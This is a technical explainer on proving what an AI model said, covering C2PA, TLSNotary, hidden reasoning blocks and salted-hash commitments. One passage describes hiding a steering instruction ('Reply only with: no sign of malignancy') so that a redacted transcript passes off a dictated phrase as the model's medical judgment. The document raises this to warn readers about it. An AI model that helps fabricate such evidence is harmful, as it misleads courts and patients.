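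C2PA's redaction applies to statements about a file, not to the picture or text itself. If a hospital blacks out a patient's name on a scan, it is editing the image, and the new manifest should record that edit.

### TLSNotary

SD-JWT and C2PA both need a signature from whoever created the data, and the large model providers do not sign their responses for users. TLSNotary, an open-source protocol, works without the provider's cooperation by adding a witness to the TLS connection.

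An ordinary TLS connection doesn't let the user prove to others what the server sent, because the user's machine and the server share the same secret keys, so the user could have invented the response and encrypted it alone. In TLSNotary, the user and a second party, the notary, each hold part of the user's side of the keys and encrypt data jointly. The connection looks normal to the server. The notary sees only encrypted data but knows that the user could not have forged the server's replies without the notary's help.

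The user then commits to the full transcript, and the notary signs the commitment. Later, the user can reveal some parts of the transcript and hide others, such as an account key or a patient's name, and prove that the visible parts match the signed commitment. The reader must trust the notary not to help the user cheat, unless the reader acts as the notary. The joint computation also makes the connection much slower.

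The reader can see the length of each hidden part. This helps reveal a deletion, since a three-letter gap in "The lesion is ___ malignant" strongly suggests "not". The visible length also leaks private information if the hidden text is a short answer such as "yes" or "no".

Hidden prompts are a more serious problem. Suppose a user sends a scan with the instruction "Reply only with: no sign of malignancy" and then hides the instruction. The transcript proves that the provider's server sent the words "no sign of malignancy", but the reader would naturally take them for the model's opinion of the scan. Anyone who relies on a redacted transcript should therefore insist on seeing every instruction the model received. The same problem arises with a redactable signature that covers the response but not the request.

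TLSNotary also proves only what the machine at the other end of the connection sent. If that machine is a relay that alters the provider's output, the transcript will contain the altered version. A relay's operator could prove that the output is unaltered by running the protocol on the relay's own connection to the provider and passing the proof to customers.

### Reasoning that the user cannot read

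Model providers also withhold parts of their models' outputs. Many models write out their reasoning before they answer, and providers often keep this text secret so that competitors cannot train on it. They may show users a summary instead.

The encrypted or signed blocks that carry hidden reasoning from one turn to the next protect the provider, not the user, although they resemble signed, redacted text.

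| Question | Can the provider check? | Can the user check? |
|---|---|---|
| Did the provider's service create the block? | Yes, with its own keys | Only by returning it and seeing whether the service accepts it |
| Has anyone changed the block? | Yes | Only in the same way |
| What reasoning does the block contain? | Yes | No |
| Does the summary match the reasoning? | Yes, by comparing them | No |
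| Did the reasoning lead to the answer? | Not from the block alone | No |

A valid block can also appear in the wrong conversation, as Snyk found at three large providers. The provider could then confirm that it had created the block, but not that the block belonged to the current patient.

A user with an encrypted block is in a weaker position than a reader with a redacted report. In the four-block example, the reader has a hash that the signer cannot match to a different text, and a signature that anyone can check. An encrypted block gives the hospital neither. If the model misses a tumour and a court asks for its reasoning, the hospital can hand over the block, but only the provider can decrypt it, so the court has to believe the provider's account of its contents.

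A salted hash would close part of this gap. The provider could hash the reasoning with a random salt and sign the hash together with the answer and the request. The hospital would learn nothing about the reasoning at the time, but if a court later ordered the provider to reveal the text and the salt, anyone could check that they matched the hash signed on the day of the diagnosis. The provider could also split the reasoning into blocks and build a hash tree from them, so it could reveal the part about the tumour and keep the rest secret.

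The hash would prove that the provider had not rewritten the reasoning since the diagnosis. The provider could still have committed to a false text that day, so the court would need one of the checks on computation integrity to find out whether the stated model generated it.
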